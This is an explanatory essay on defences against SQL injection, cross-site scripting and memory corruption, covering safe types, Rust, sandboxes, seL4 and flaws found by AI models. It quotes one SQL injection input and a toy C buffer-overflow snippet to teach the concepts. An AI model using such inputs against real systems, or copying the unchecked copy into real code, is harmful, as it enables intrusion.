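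Google therefore had the compiler, which turns source code into a working program, check the rule. Most programming languages give each piece of data a type, such as number or text, and a compiler can reject code that supplies the wrong type. *Safe Coding* (Kern, 2025) describes a type called TrustedSqlString. Google's database functions accept only queries of this type, and programmers can build one only from text written in the program itself or from another trusted source. The type has no operation for adding a visitor's input, so a programmer who tries to paste that input into the query gets an error message and has to use a parameter instead.

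A type called SafeHtml does the same for web pages. Functions that insert HTML into a page accept only SafeHtml, and a programmer can obtain it in four ways:

- from text written in the program
- from an automatic escaping template
- from a sanitiser, which strips out anything that could run as a script
- by an explicit override, which a security expert must approve

The compiler cannot check everything, because JavaScript does not enforce types when a program runs. Trusted Types, which Google proposed as a web standard, move the check into the browser. Once a website turns them on, the browser's dangerous functions reject ordinary text and accept only values that have passed through a policy, a short piece of code in which the website's programmers define what is safe. According to web.dev's *Prevent DOM-based cross-site scripting vulnerabilities with Trusted Types*, this makes the functions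 "secure by default". A policy that approves everything would give no protection, but reviewers can check a few policies far more easily than every line of a large website.

A determined programmer can defeat these systems. One trick Kern describes is to rebuild an attacker's text letter by letter from a list of approved letters. In Google's experience this is not a significant problem, because such code looks obviously wrong and these systems exist to catch honest mistakes. They would not be enough against hostile programmers.

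### Google's results

Around 2014 Google found tens of XSS flaws a year in each large application such as Gmail, according to Kern's *Developer Ecosystems for Software Safety* (2024). A decade later the yearly total for all applications built on its safe frameworks was in the low single digits. Kern's 2025 report gives an average, over several years, of less than one XSS report a year for hundreds of complex applications combined. Google Photos, which used the safe frameworks from the start, has never had one. The hundreds of applications that use the safe database functions have had no SQL injection reports for more than a decade.

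Wang and colleagues also followed a single product whose web pages were written by a few dozen programmers. Researchers found 10 DOM-based XSS flaws in the year before the team adopted the safe functions, 2 in the year of the change and 1 in the year after. PortSwigger's *Google checks rise of DOM XSS with Trusted Types* reports that by 2021 Google had seen no such flaws in the applications it had moved to Trusted Types since 2019.

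These figures come from Google's own engineers and count only the flaws that somebody reported, but Google has paid outsiders millions of dollars for reports of XSS, so people had good reason to look. Other security measures may explain part of the decline, though Wang and colleagues offer some evidence that they don't explain all of it. From 2018, DOM-based XSS made up a shrinking share of the serious flaws that outsiders reported, while a growing share of the remaining XSS flaws came from old code that did not use the safe functions. Both trends would be expected if the safe functions caused most of the decline.

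Following the rules took a modest amount of work for a company of Google's size. By the end of 2020, fewer than 1% of its more than one million JavaScript files had an exemption, and most of those were old. Programmers submitted about 10,000 changes involving JavaScript each week, but the security team received fewer than eight exemption requests a week during the first five months of large-scale use. A smaller organisation might find the change harder, since Google keeps its code in one shared store and can make every programmer use the same compiler.

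### Why SQL injection still ranks second

SQL injection peaked around 2010 and is now rare in websites, according to David C, who credits better defaults and methods after a decade of breaches. But MITRE, a non-profit that maintains standard lists of software flaws, ranks cross-site scripting first and SQL injection second in its *2025 CWE Top 25 Most Dangerous Software Weaknesses* (2025). SQL injection was third the year before. Joe (2025) pointed out on a mailing list that both weaknesses have been in the Top 25 since 2009.

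The two accounts measure different things. MITRE compiled its ranking from the weaknesses behind 39,080 public vulnerability records, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *Top 25 Most Dangerous Software Weaknesses of 2025 Revealed* (2025). Those records mostly concern products that many organisations install, such as a plug-in for a blog or a file-transfer server. A flaw in one company's own website usually gets no record. A plug-in with few users can add as much to the count as a famous product, and the ranking does not show what share of websites has a given weakness. A weakness can also rise in the ranking because others fall. Writing outside the bounds of memory, for example, dropped from second place to fifth.

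MITRE also reports how many flaws of each type appear in a US government catalogue of vulnerabilities that attackers are known to have used. SQL injection accounts for 4 and cross-site scripting for 7. Operating-system command injection ranks only ninth but accounts for 20. It involves the same mistake, with a program pasting a stranger's text into a command for the computer it runs on.

The SQL injection flaws that remain can still cause enormous damage. In May 2023 a criminal group called Cl0p exploited one in MOVEit Transfer, a product for exchanging sensitive files, and stole data from more than 2,000 organisations. Parameterised queries had been available for many years, but a single unsafe query in the product exposed all of its customers at once.

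Parameters prevent nearly all SQL injection where programmers use them, but nothing forces programmers to use them. Old programs still contain queries with user input pasted in, and many languages still make pasting as easy as using a parameter. Some parts of a query cannot be parameters. OWASP's *C3* (2018) warns that these parts differ between databases and need exact checks or careful escaping by hand. A common example is a page that lets visitors choose which column to sort by. A placeholder can hold a value but not a column name, so the program should compare the visitor's choice with a fixed list of names and use its own copy of the matching name.

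Parameterised queries pass all three tests for a win set out earlier, but they do not stop well-formed requests for data the visitor has no right to see. If a visitor changes the invoice number in a web address from 1043 to 1044, a parameterised query will treat 1044 as an ordinary value and fetch the invoice, even if it belongs to someone else. The program has to check whether the visitor is allowed to see it. Missing authorisation, the failure to make such checks, rose from ninth to fourth in MITRE's ranking.

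### The need for a formal grammar

Parameterised queries are possible because SQL has a formal grammar, a set of rules that determines which strings are valid queries and how each one breaks down into parts. Without these rules, developers could not specify exactly what a visitor may supply, and "treat this as data" would have no precise meaning.

Su and Wassermann used the grammar to define injection. In a legitimate query, each input fills exactly one branch of the parse tree, as "swordfish" does. The input `' OR 'a'='a` doesn't, because it includes the end of one value, an operator and parts of a new comparison. Their tool, SQLCHECK, marks where each input begins and ends, parses the finished query and blocks the query if any input doesn't fill exactly one branch. On lists of real attacks and legitimate inputs, most of them from an independent research group, SQLCHECK made no errors and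 took about 3 milliseconds per query.

Ray and Ligatti later found that this definition was slightly wrong. Suppose a query compares a PIN with the visitor's input, and the visitor types `exit()`. The input fills exactly one branch, so the definition allows it, but it is a function call that might shut down the database. The definition also counts some harmless queries as attacks, such as one that joins a file name and an extension from separate inputs into a single piece of text. Users of SQLCHECK could forbid function calls, but they would have to know in advance which forms to forbid.

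Ray and Ligatti proposed that input is harmless if it ends up only inside closed values, such as numbers or pieces of text, which contain no variables and leave nothing to compute. This definition works for any language that precisely defines what counts as a value. Parameterised queries already satisfied this better definition, because a placeholder accepts only a value. If someone entered `exit()` as a PIN, the database would look for a PIN made up of those six characters.

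HTML is less strict than SQL because browsers accept badly formed pages, and some guess a file's type from its contents. Wang and colleagues had to read the web standards by hand to list the functions that can turn text into a running script, and considered it unrealistic to cover every browser's undocumented behaviour. Someone therefore has to maintain the list their defence uses, although it needs additions much less often than new attack texts appear.

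David C doubts that prompt injection will ever have a fix like the parameterised query, because ordinary English has no grammar that separates commands from data.

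## Memory-safe languages

Memory-safe languages prevent a program from reading or writing memory outside the data it is using. Java, Swift, Python and Rust are memory-safe, but C and C++ are not. Programmers have written most operating systems, browsers and network tools in C and C++ because these languages are fast and give direct control over the hardware. This has led to decades of memory corruption, which causes about 70% of vulnerabilities according to an industry norm cited by Google. Parameterised queries only have to protect the places where a program queries a database, but a C program can corrupt memory almost anywhere, so a comparable fix has to cover the whole language.

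### Two ways to corrupt memory

Suppose a C program keeps a 12-byte record for each visitor. Eight bytes hold the visitor's name, and four hold a number that is zero for everyone except administrators.

```
struct account {
    char name[8];
    int  is_admin;
};

strcpy(a->name, input);
```

The last line copies the visitor's input into the name field without checking the input's length. If the visitor types nine letters, the ninth lands in the first byte of `is_admin`. Because `is_admin` is no longer zero, the program treats the visitor as an administrator. This is called a buffer overflow. A buffer is a block of memory set aside for a piece of data.

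The 17-year-old FreeBSD flaw that Mythos Preview exploited was the same kind of mistake. According to Carlini and colleagues, FreeBSD copied data from a network packet into a 96-byte space in a buffer after checking only that the data was no longer than 400 bytes. An attacker could therefore overwrite up to 304 bytes past the end of the buffer. This kind of memory also holds return addresses, which tell the processor where to continue when a function ends. By overwriting them, the attacker could make the processor run fragments of FreeBSD's own code in a new order.

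The other common mistake is use-after-free. Suppose the visitor logs out and the program frees the 12-byte record, making its memory available for reuse. Another part of the program still holds a pointer to the record, its address in memory. The visitor then sends a 12-character message, and the program happens to store it in the same 12 bytes. When the other part of the program follows its old pointer to check `is_admin`, it reads the last four characters of the message, which the visitor chose.

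### Patching one flaw at a time

In 2024 Google divided the industry's responses to memory corruption into four generations. Companies first patched flaws as people reported them. They then added mitigations, which make flaws harder to exploit, and later built tools to find flaws before attackers did. The fourth generation uses languages and libraries that prevent programmers from creating the flaws.

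Developers cannot patch flaws fast enough when finding them becomes easy. Anthropic (2026) publishes a tally of the vulnerabilities its models have found in open-source software, which stood as follows on 2 November 2026:

| Stage | Number of findings |
|---|---|
| Candidates found by the models | 37,966 |
| Reviewed by outside security firms | 6,376 |
| Confirmed as real by those firms | 6,009 |
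| Reported to the software's maintainers | 5,087 |
| Known to be patched | 629 |

The maintainers had patched about 12% of the flaws reported to them. That figure will rise, since many reports were recent and patches take time to write. Some of the reports may also be false alarms, because Anthropic sent 3,225 of them directly to maintainers without an outside review. Once a patch is finished, it protects only those who install it. The largest backlog was at the start of the process, where about 28,000 candidates were still waiting for a person to examine them. Anthropic describes this human review as the step that limits the whole process.

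About two thirds of the findings with a public vulnerability record are out-of-bounds accesses or uses after free. This is partly because Carlini and colleagues concentrated on memory corruption, which they chose since automatic tools can confirm it with almost no false alarms.

In Garfinkel and Dafoe's model, heavy investment in finding flaws eventually favours the defender. The tally shows that this holds only if defenders repair flaws about as fast as they find them. Otherwise, an attacker with a similar language model can find the same flaws before they are patched.

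### Mitigations and Apple's memory tags

Mitigations are meant to keep attackers from exploiting the flaws that remain in a program. For example, a stack canary is a secret value that the compiler places between a buffer and the return address. An overflow that reaches the address also changes the canary, and the program stops when it detects the change.

A mitigation helps only where it is switched on. FreeBSD's compiler setting added canaries only to functions with character buffers, so the vulnerable function, whose buffer was declared as an array of integers, had none. FreeBSD also loaded its kernel at a predictable address, so the attacker knew where to find the code fragments. Carlini and colleagues write that they might have dismissed the flaw as unexploitable if the model had not exploited it.

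The most ambitious mitigation so far is in hardware. Apple's *Memory Integrity Enforcement* (2025) describes a system that took the company five years to build. It works by attaching secret tags to memory:

1. When a program asks for a block of memory, the system gives the block a tag and puts the same tag in the pointer to it.
2. Each time the program uses the pointer, the processor compares the two tags and blocks the access if they differ.
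3. Neighbouring blocks have different tags, so an overflow from one block into the next fails.
4. The system changes a block's tag when it reuses the memory, so an old pointer no longer works.

A tag is four bits long, so a guess is right one time in 16. But a wrong guess normally crashes the program, so an attacker would rather learn the tag first. Researchers had shown that tiny timing differences could reveal tags on Google's Pixel phones, and Apple designed its chips to avoid this leak.

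The tags would not stop the nine-letter name in the earlier example, because the name and `is_admin` are in the same block and share a tag. Apple acknowledges that the tags don't stop overflows within a block, but calls such overflows extremely rare. Its own attack team, which worked on the system from 2020 to 2025, tried to rebuild attacks that spyware companies had used against iPhones, and also picked newer flaws that seemed most likely to get through. The team could not restore any of the old attacks, even by swapping in new flaws.

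In May 2026 Calif, a small outside security company, announced the first public attack of this kind on the kernel of a Mac protected by the tags. One of its researchers found the flaws on 25 April, and the team had a working exploit by 1 May. The exploit gives an ordinary user full administrator control. Mythos Preview found the flaws quickly because they belonged to known types, and it helped throughout the work on the exploit. Calif credits human expertise with getting past the new protection.

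The first flaw let a malicious file server make the kernel treat one type of record as another by sending an unexpected kind of reply, according to Calif's *Apple MIE exploitation challenge*. The second made the kernel hand over a large block of memory without clearing it, revealing whatever the block had held before. Neither flaw was an overflow or a use-after-free, and Apple fixed both in macOS 26.6. iTnews' *Apple rains on MIE-bypassing iPhone jailbreak parade with iOS update* reports that researchers have also got past the protection on an iPhone, and that Apple has issued an update.

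Memory tags are therefore a form of friction, though they make attacks much harder. They broke every old attack that Apple tried to rebuild, and Calif needed experts, a frontier model and two suitable flaws to get round them. Apple had aimed to raise the cost of spyware and did not promise perfect security. But the defence depends on Apple repairing each suitable flaw, and models are making those flaws easier to find. Carlini and colleagues also expect mitigations that rely on tedium to weaken, because a model can work through tedious steps quickly.

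### Searching for flaws in C

Fuzzing, the best-known way to search for memory corruption, feeds a program millions of random inputs and watches for crashes. It has found many flaws, but it easily misses those that only an unusual input triggers.

FFmpeg, a video decoder, contained a memory-safety flaw that fuzzing and human review had missed for 16 years. The decoder divides each frame of video into slices and keeps a table of which slice each part belongs to. In that table, the number 65,535 means "no slice". Ordinary frames have few slices, so none is numbered that high. Mythos Preview found that a frame with 65,536 slices would include one numbered 65,535, and that the decoder would then write outside its buffer. Carlini and colleagues believe the flaw would be hard to exploit. Several hundred runs of the model, costing roughly $10,000, also found other important flaws in FFmpeg.

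curl, a tool for transferring data that runs on phones, cars and games consoles, is the best argument that careful programmers can manage without a new language. Its lead developer, Daniel Stenberg, describes what happened when someone scanned its 178,000 lines of C with the same model in *Mythos finds a curl vulnerability* (2026). The model reported five "confirmed" vulnerabilities. The curl team decided that three were false alarms, one was an ordinary bug and one was a real vulnerability of low severity. None involved memory corruption.

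One reason is that other AI tools had already led to between 200 and 300 bug fixes in curl over the previous eight to ten months, including perhaps a dozen published vulnerabilities. Stenberg saw no sign that Mythos Preview was much better than those tools, and attributed the excitement about it mainly to marketing. That is a fair reading of the curl result, but curl is unusually well tested, so the result is a poor measure of how many flaws a model can find in other programs.

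Another reason, according to the scan's report, is that curl's programmers follow rules that prevent common mistakes. For example, buffers that grow have a maximum size, and every function that reads a number takes an explicit upper limit. By following these rules, the programmers do by hand some of what a memory-safe language does automatically. Curl has also had years of fuzzing and several paid audits, and its programmers have written each line of the present code about four times on average. Few C projects get this much attention, and even in those that do, a new contributor can forget a rule.

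### Bounds checks and ownership

Memory-safe languages prevent overflows with bounds checks. An array (a row of values in memory) is stored with its length, and the program compares each position with that length before reading or writing. In the earlier example, the name would be an array of length eight. An attempt to write a ninth letter would stop the program or return an error, and `is_admin` would stay zero. The compiler can leave out a check when it can prove that the position is valid, so checking adds little running time. An attacker may still be able to crash the program by triggering a failed check, but can no longer use an overflow to take it over.

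Use-after-free is harder to prevent. Java, Python and many other languages use a garbage collector, a part of the running system that frees a piece of memory only once nothing in the program can reach it. This works well, but the collector takes up time and memory, and it is a poor fit for a kernel or a device driver. Rust instead has the compiler check the use of memory before the program ever runs. The compiler enforces these rules:

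- Each value has exactly one owner, usually a variable. When the owner goes out of use, the program frees the value's memory.
- Assigning the value to another variable can transfer ownership, after which the program may no longer use the old variable.
- Other code can borrow the value through a reference, but no reference may outlast the value.
- At any moment a value may have many references that only read it, or one that can change it, but not both.

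The following program breaks the third rule.

```
let account = Account::new("alice");
let session = &account;
drop(account);
println!("{}", session.is_admin);
```

The first line creates a record owned by `account`, and the second lets `session` borrow it. The third frees the record, and the fourth tries to read it through `session`. A C compiler would accept the equivalent code. The Rust compiler rejects the program, reporting that it gives up `account` while `session` is still borrowing it.

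The last rule prevents a subtler mistake. When a list outgrows its block of memory, the program may move it to a larger block and free the old one. Any existing reference to an item would then point to freed memory. Adding an item changes the list, so the compiler does not allow it while other code still holds such a reference.

Rust's other checks also cover the two mistakes behind Calif's attack. Ordinary Rust code cannot treat one type of record as another or read memory before the program has stored a value there.

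Like parameterised queries, these checks are a hard barrier, provided the compiler is correct and the code marked "unsafe" contains no mistakes.

### What unsafe code permits

Some tasks are impossible under Rust's rules. A device driver has to write to specific hardware addresses, and a program that calls a C library has to rely on the pointers the library returns. Rust lets programmers put such code in a block marked `unsafe`, where they can follow a raw pointer, which is an address the compiler has not checked, and call functions whose safety it cannot verify.

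The other checks still apply inside an unsafe block, including the borrowing rules for ordinary references and bounds checks on ordinary arrays. Programmers usually wrap the block in a function that the rest of the program can call safely, so a reviewer can check the block's assumptions in one place. The trusted computing base for memory safety shrinks from the whole program to the compiler, the unsafe blocks, the code those blocks rely on, and any libraries in other languages.

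### Android's experience

Google's Android operating system offers the best evidence of how changing languages affects a large project. Around 2019 the Android team began writing more of its new code in memory-safe languages, including Java, Kotlin and, later, Rust, while leaving most of the old C and C++ in place. According to Google, memory-safety flaws fell from 76% of Android's vulnerabilities in 2019 to 24% in 2024. Vander Stoep's *Rust in Android* (2025) reports that the share fell below 20% in 2025.

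The number of memory-safety flaws also fell, apart from a slight rise in 2023, so their share didn't fall merely because other kinds of flaw became more common. Google projected 36 for the whole of 2024, based on 27 by September. The change of language may not explain the whole decline, because the team was also making its old code safer. Google suggests this as a possible reason the results were better than its simulation had predicted.

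It may seem odd that flaws should become rare while most of the code is still unsafe. Google's explanation is that old code has fewer flaws left in it. Suppose that each flaw has the same chance of being found and fixed in any given year, however old it is. The number of flaws per line then falls exponentially:

d(t) = d(0) × e^(−t/τ)

Here d(0) is the number of flaws per line in new code, t is the age of the code in years and τ is the mean lifetime of a flaw. Google uses a mean lifetime of 2.5 years, based on Android and the Chromium browser. For five-year-old code, t/τ is then 2, so it has e², or about 7.4, times fewer flaws per line than new code. Using lifetimes that Alexopoulos and colleagues measured in open-source projects, Google also gives a lower ratio of 3.4, which corresponds to a mean lifetime of about 4.1 years.

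The same formula shows why a team can leave its old code alone. Suppose programmers add 1,000 flaws a year and flaws last 2.5 years on average. The total settles at 2,500, when flaws are fixed as fast as they are added. If all new code is memory-safe from then on, about 340 of those flaws remain after five years, even if nobody rewrites the old code. Rewriting the old code first would be a poor use of effort, because it has the fewest flaws per line.

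Projects usually move to memory-safe languages gradually. Google simulated a project that doubles in size every six years and takes ten years to switch its new code to safe languages. Unsafe code still grew, but the number of memory-safety flaws dropped sharply, because less and less of the unsafe code was new. To make a gradual switch practical, Google has invested in tools that let Rust and C++ code work together.

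The decay happens only if people keep finding and fixing flaws. Measured lifetimes also leave out flaws that nobody has found yet. With a mean lifetime of 2.5 years, only about one flaw in 900 would last 17 years, as the FreeBSD flaw did. Carlini and colleagues report that many of the flaws Mythos Preview found were ten or twenty years old. These came from other projects, where flaws may last longer than in Android, but they suggest that the formula underestimates how many flaws survive in old code. A team that stops writing unsafe code still has to maintain the unsafe code it already has.

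### Is Rust a thousand times safer?

Vander Stoep estimates that Android's Rust code has more than 1,000 times fewer memory-safety vulnerabilities per line than its C and C++ code. Google has found one potential memory-safety vulnerability in Android's roughly 5 million lines of Rust, or 0.2 per million lines. The historical rate for C and C++ is about 1,000 per million lines, which is about 5,000 times as high.

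The one vulnerability was a buffer overflow in CrabbyAVIF, an image decoder. Google fixed it before any public release. The memory-safe language had not prevented the overflow, but an older kind of mitigation made it unexploitable on phones that use Scudo, Android's standard memory allocator. Scudo surrounds large blocks of memory with pages that no program may touch. The overflow ran into one of these pages and caused a crash, which also helped Google notice it.

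An estimate based on a single event is imprecise. One discovery would still be plausible if the expected number were as high as 5.6. That would mean about 1.1 vulnerabilities per million lines, still roughly 900 times fewer than in the historical C and C++ code.

The choice of comparison is a bigger problem, because the historical figure covers flaws found over many years, while most of the Rust is fairly new and may contain flaws that nobody has had time to find. If the average line of Rust were two years old and its flaws had the usual mean lifetime, people would have found about 55% of them by now. Correcting for this would only double the Rust figure, but the C and C++ figure also describes the code's past rather than its present state. For example, curl has published 188 vulnerabilities of all kinds in its history, or about 1,070 per million lines of its present code, yet the Mythos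 Preview scan of that code found no memory corruption. A fairer test would compare new Rust with equally new C++ written by the same teams for similar tasks.

The evidence from unsafe blocks is stronger. They make up about 4% of Android's Rust, or 200,000 lines. If those lines were as prone to flaws as the historical C and C++ code, they would contain about 200 memory-safety vulnerabilities. Google has found one in all 5 million lines of Rust. The improvement is therefore clearly very large, though the exact factor of 1,000 is doubtful.

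### Faster reviews and fewer rollbacks

Adopting Rust seems to have sped up Android's programmers, whereas security measures often slow programmers down, which gives companies a reason to avoid them. Vander Stoep compares Rust and C++ changes of similar size, written by Google's Android developers, many of whom use both languages. The Rust changes needed about 20% fewer revisions and spent about 25% less time in review. Among medium and large changes, the team rolled back Rust changes about a quarter as often as C++ changes. A rollback removes an accepted change that has caused trouble, and it can delay several other teams.

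The choice of language may not explain all of the difference, because developers may choose Rust for new, self-contained components and C++ for awkward changes to old ones. The comparison also leaves out the effort of learning Rust, although Vander Stoep suspects that growing expertise explains why Rust reviews became faster between 2023 and 2024. Still, by 2025 Android's developers were adding slightly more Rust than C++ on balance. It is easier to persuade a company to adopt a defence that also saves its programmers time.

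### Flaws in memory-safe programs

Carlini and colleagues report a finding that tests the assumption about unsafe code. Mythos Preview found memory corruption in a virtual machine monitor written in a memory-safe language. Cloud companies use such monitors to run several customers' virtual machines on one physical computer while keeping them apart. A monitor has to handle raw memory addresses to communicate with the hardware, so it cannot avoid unsafe operations. The flaw was in one of these operations, and it let a malicious customer write out of bounds in the monitor's own memory.

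An attacker could easily crash the monitor this way. The model could not build a working exploit that did more, though Carlini and colleagues think the flaw might be useful in combination with others. They did not name the product, but it may have been Firecracker, Amazon's monitor, which is written in Rust. On the day of their report, AWS disclosed an out-of-bounds write in Firecracker (*CVE-2026-5747*, 2026). A customer could trigger it by changing the settings of a device already in use, and AWS warned that it might allow an attacker to run code on the host computer.

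Programs that combine languages carry a similar risk. Anthropic's tally includes a use-after-free in a Rust file of Suricata, a network monitoring program that mixes Rust with C. Where the two languages meet, the Rust compiler cannot check how long the C code will keep a piece of memory valid.

Both cases fit the stated assumption, and neither shows a way to corrupt memory through ordinary safe code. But they mean defenders should focus their reviews on unsafe blocks and the connections between languages, because attackers with good models will search there too.

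Memory safety does not prevent errors in a program's logic. The tally also lists a critical flaw in Rocket.Chat, a messaging system, that let an attacker bypass the login and gain administrator rights. Another critical flaw, in the publishing system Ghost, let any visitor read the database through SQL injection. Both products are written mainly in JavaScript or TypeScript, which are memory-safe.

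## Sandboxes and verified kernels

A sandbox limits the damage when part of a system fails. Parameterised queries and memory-safe languages prevent particular mistakes, but every large program contains others. A sandbox's designer therefore assumes that an attacker will take over some component, and restricts what that component can do. The protection depends on the code that enforces the restrictions, which runs to millions of lines in Linux but fewer than 10,000 in seL4, a small operating-system kernel with a mathematical proof of correctness. In 2026 AI models found ways to escape several of the most widely used sandboxes.

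### How a browser contains a hostile page

A browser has to run code from strangers. Each web page can include its own scripts, fonts, images and video, and the software that handles them is large and mostly written in C and C++. Google's Chrome, released in 2008, split this work between separate processes, which are running programs that normally cannot read each other's memory. Other browsers now do the same. The browser's designers assume that a hostile page will eventually take over the renderer process, which draws the page and runs its scripts.

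1. When the browser starts a renderer, it gives up nearly all of the renderer's rights. The renderer cannot open the user's files, start other programs or connect to the network.
2. If the page needs something from outside, such as an image from a server, the renderer sends a request to a more privileged process.
3. The privileged process checks whether this renderer may have the image, fetches it and passes it back.

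An attacker who controls the renderer can send the privileged process any request, including ones no legitimate page would produce, but cannot read a file without escaping the sandbox. An escape usually requires a second flaw, either in how the privileged process handles requests or in the operating system's kernel.

At first this design protected the user's computer better than the user's accounts. One renderer could hold pages from several websites, for example when a hostile page displayed a bank's page in a frame. An attacker who took over that renderer could read the bank's page from its memory without escaping the sandbox. In 2018 researchers disclosed Spectre, a weakness in processors that let a script work out the contents of its own process's memory from tiny differences in timing. Google responded by turning on site isolation for nearly all desktop users of Chrome. Each site now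 gets its own process, and the privileged process withholds one site's cookies and private pages from another site's renderer. Site isolation increased Chrome's memory use by about 10%. Firefox adopted site isolation in 2021.

The Hacker News' *Anthropic's Unreleased AI Model Chains Flaws* (2026) describes an exploit in Apple's Safari that let any website read data from other sites where the visitor was signed in, such as an email or bank account. The attacker didn't need access to the visitor's files. Apple fixed the flaws it used in June.

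Chromium, the open-source project behind Chrome, has a simple rule for deciding where code should run. Under its Rule of 2, a piece of code may have at most two of these three properties:

- It processes input from an untrustworthy source.
- Its programmers wrote it in an unsafe language, such as C or C++.
- It runs with high privileges.

A C++ program that decodes images from the web handles untrusted input in a memory-unsafe language, so the rule requires it to run in a sandbox. If a privileged process has to read the same images, programmers should write the decoder in a memory-safe language. Either a sandbox or a safe language satisfies the rule, which helps a team with old code because moving a decoder into a sandbox is often easier than rewriting it.

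### Shared kernels and virtual machines

A process sandbox relies on the kernel to enforce its limits. The Linux kernel has roughly 40 million lines of code, and although any one computer uses only part of it, a flaw in that part can give a sandboxed program control of the whole machine. Browsers reduce the danger by blocking most of the requests a renderer could otherwise make to the kernel.

Containers, which cloud companies use to run many customers' programs on one computer, usually let those programs reach more of the kernel. Each container has its own view of the files and running programs, but they all share one kernel. In 2026 an AI system from the security company Theori found a kernel flaw called Copy Fail in about an hour, according to Bugcrowd, which runs rewards programmes for security researchers. The flaw gave any logged-in user full administrator (root) control on most of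 the popular versions of Linux. Techzine reports that it also let attackers break out of containers, and that criminals or spies had already used it.

A virtual machine gives each customer a simulated computer with its own kernel. An attacker who takes over that kernel controls only the simulated computer, and must still break through the monitor that runs it. Bugcrowd lists Amazon's Firecracker as unaffected by Copy Fail, because its customers do not share the host's kernel. The monitor can have flaws too, like the out-of-bounds write in Firecracker described earlier, but it has far less code to check than Linux.

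### Layers that fail together

An attack on a browser may have to get through the renderer, the sandbox and the kernel's own protections. People often assume that the difficulty multiplies with each layer. Suppose that on any given day there is a 10% chance that an attacker holds a working exploit for each of three layers. If the three chances are independent, the chance of getting through all of them is

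0.1 × 0.1 × 0.1 = 0.001, or one in 1,000.

Now suppose that on 2% of days the attacker has a single flaw that defeats all three layers, perhaps in a kernel that they all rely on. Each layer on its own still fails 10% of the time, so on the remaining days its chance of failing must be about 8.2%. The chance of getting through all three becomes

0.02 + 0.98 × 0.082³ ≈ 0.0205, or about one in 49.

The system is now about 20 times easier to break, although no single layer has become weaker. More layers of the same kind would hardly help. With six layers, the attacker's chance would be one in a million if the layers failed independently, but the shared flaw would keep it at 2%.

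Better attackers have a similar effect even when the layers share no flaw, because they are more likely to defeat each one. If a new model triples the chance of defeating each of three independent layers, from 10% to 30%, the chance of defeating all three rises 27-fold, from 0.1% to 2.7%.

The attacker's effort is even less likely to multiply across layers. Suppose one attempt in 100 succeeds against each of three layers. An attacker who learned only whether the whole chain had worked would need about a million attempts. In practice, an attacker can copy the software, study each layer separately and save every success, which takes about 300 attempts in all. With encryption, by contrast, an attacker who has guessed half a key correctly gets no sign of it.

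Layers also help defenders because the attacker needs every flaw in the chain to stay open at once. Fixing any one of them breaks the attack until the attacker finds a replacement.

### The proof behind seL4

Because all the other layers depend on the kernel, one defense is to make it small enough to prove correct. Most kernels include device drivers, file systems and network code, all running with full privileges. seL4 is a microkernel, which keeps only the functions that need those privileges, such as dividing up memory and passing messages between programs. Drivers and file systems run outside it as ordinary programs. The version its developers first proved correct had about 8,700 lines of C and 600 lines of assembly.

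Gerwin Klein, Gernot Heiser and colleagues at NICTA, an Australian research institute, published that proof in 2009. It has three parts:

1. A specification describes precisely what each operation of the kernel may do. For example, it states how one program can give another access to a block of memory. seL4 controls access with capabilities, the kind of token that Hardy recommended after the compiler overwrote the billing file.
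2. A theorem relates the C code to the specification. If C is the set of everything the code can do and S is the set of everything the specification allows, the theorem is C ⊆ S, meaning that the code never does anything outside the specification.
3. A program called Isabelle checks every step of the argument, so a reader does not have to trust the people who wrote it.

The theorem covers every possible input, including attacks nobody has thought of. It rules out buffer overflows and use-after-free bugs in the kernel's C code, as well as logic errors, which memory-safe languages do not prevent. By 2013 the team had also proved that a program cannot read or change another program's data without the right capabilities. The team had also extended the proof to the compiled code for some processors, so users there no longer had to assume the compiler was correct.

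Designing and writing the kernel took a little over two person-years, and the proof took about 20. Roughly half of the proof effort went into tools and methods that later projects could reuse. The proof was about 200,000 lines long, or 23 lines for each line of C, and it uncovered 144 defects that testing had missed.

The proof still assumes that the processor behaves as its manual describes and that the assembly code and startup code are correct. Devices that can write directly to memory need separate controls. Someone must also give each program the right capabilities, because the kernel enforces whatever assignment it is given, even a bad one. The secrecy guarantees do not cover information that leaks through timing. In 2018 the Meltdown flaw in Intel processors let ordinary programs read kernel memory through such a leak, and seL4 needed a workaround on those processors, as other kernels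 did.

The US military's research agency, DARPA, tested the approach on Little Bird, a Boeing helicopter that can fly without a pilot. Engineers rebuilt its mission computer so that seL4 separated the important functions from a virtual machine that ran Linux and handled the camera. In 2015 a team of professional hackers had six weeks to attack the helicopter. They began with root access to the camera's virtual machine, more access than most real attackers would start with, but could not break out of it or interfere with the flight. One test by one team is limited evidence, and it predates today's AI models. The proof is more important evidence because it does not depend on the attacker's skill.

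Few organisations have used seL4 as a general replacement for Linux, partly because it lacks Linux's wide range of drivers and programs. Programmers who change the kernel must also update its proof. AI models have begun to reduce the effort that proofs require. *LLMs are making formal software verification feasible at a much larger scale* (Anthropic, 2026) describes using Claude to prove security properties of the compiled code of 123 open-source libraries. The proofs came to 180 million lines (Smith, *Claude Writes 180 Million Lines of Proofs*, 2026), about 900 times as many as seL4's original proof.

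No person could read a proof that long, but a proof checker can verify it, so people need to read only the statement of what it proves. That statement is narrower than seL4's. EconoTimes' *Anthropic Details Claude's No-Crash Proofs for 239 Fuzz-Test Entry Points* (2026) reports that the guarantees cover 239 ways of calling the libraries, with inputs under 64 megabytes, on a modelled processor and operating system. Within those limits, a program will exit normally, without a crash or a memory-safety error. It may still give a wrong answer, which a full proof like seL4's would rule out.

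### Firefox's 423 repairs

Browsers are far too large for a proof like seL4's, so their developers still have to find and fix flaws. Throughout 2025, Firefox's developers fixed 20 to 30 security bugs a month. In April 2026 they fixed 423, according to Mozilla's *Behind the Scenes Hardening Firefox with Claude Mythos Preview*. Mozilla credits Mythos Preview with 271 of them, all fixed in Firefox 150. Outsiders reported another 41, and Mozilla's staff found the remaining 111 using both AI models and older methods.

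Mozilla rated 180 of the 271 bugs as high severity, 80 as moderate and 11 as low. A high rating means ordinary browsing could trigger the bug, whether or not anyone has built an attack. One such bug is usually not enough to compromise the browser, because the attacker would still be confined to a sandbox. Mozilla treats memory errors as exploitable without checking each one, so its engineers can spend their time fixing bugs.

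Some of the bugs were sandbox escapes, which fuzzing rarely finds. Mozilla had the models look for them one layer at a time, as a patient attacker would. The models could assume that an attacker had already taken over a content process, Firefox's name for a renderer. A model could rewrite any Firefox code that ran inside the sandbox, and then had to find a way into the privileged parent process.

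One of the flaws let a hijacked content process send the parent any image to use as wallpaper. If the image decoder also had a flaw, the attacker could use it to escape the sandbox. Decoding an untrusted image in C or C++ with high privileges breaks the Rule of 2. Another flaw was in the code that checks data leaving a smaller sandbox, which Firefox puts around third-party libraries.

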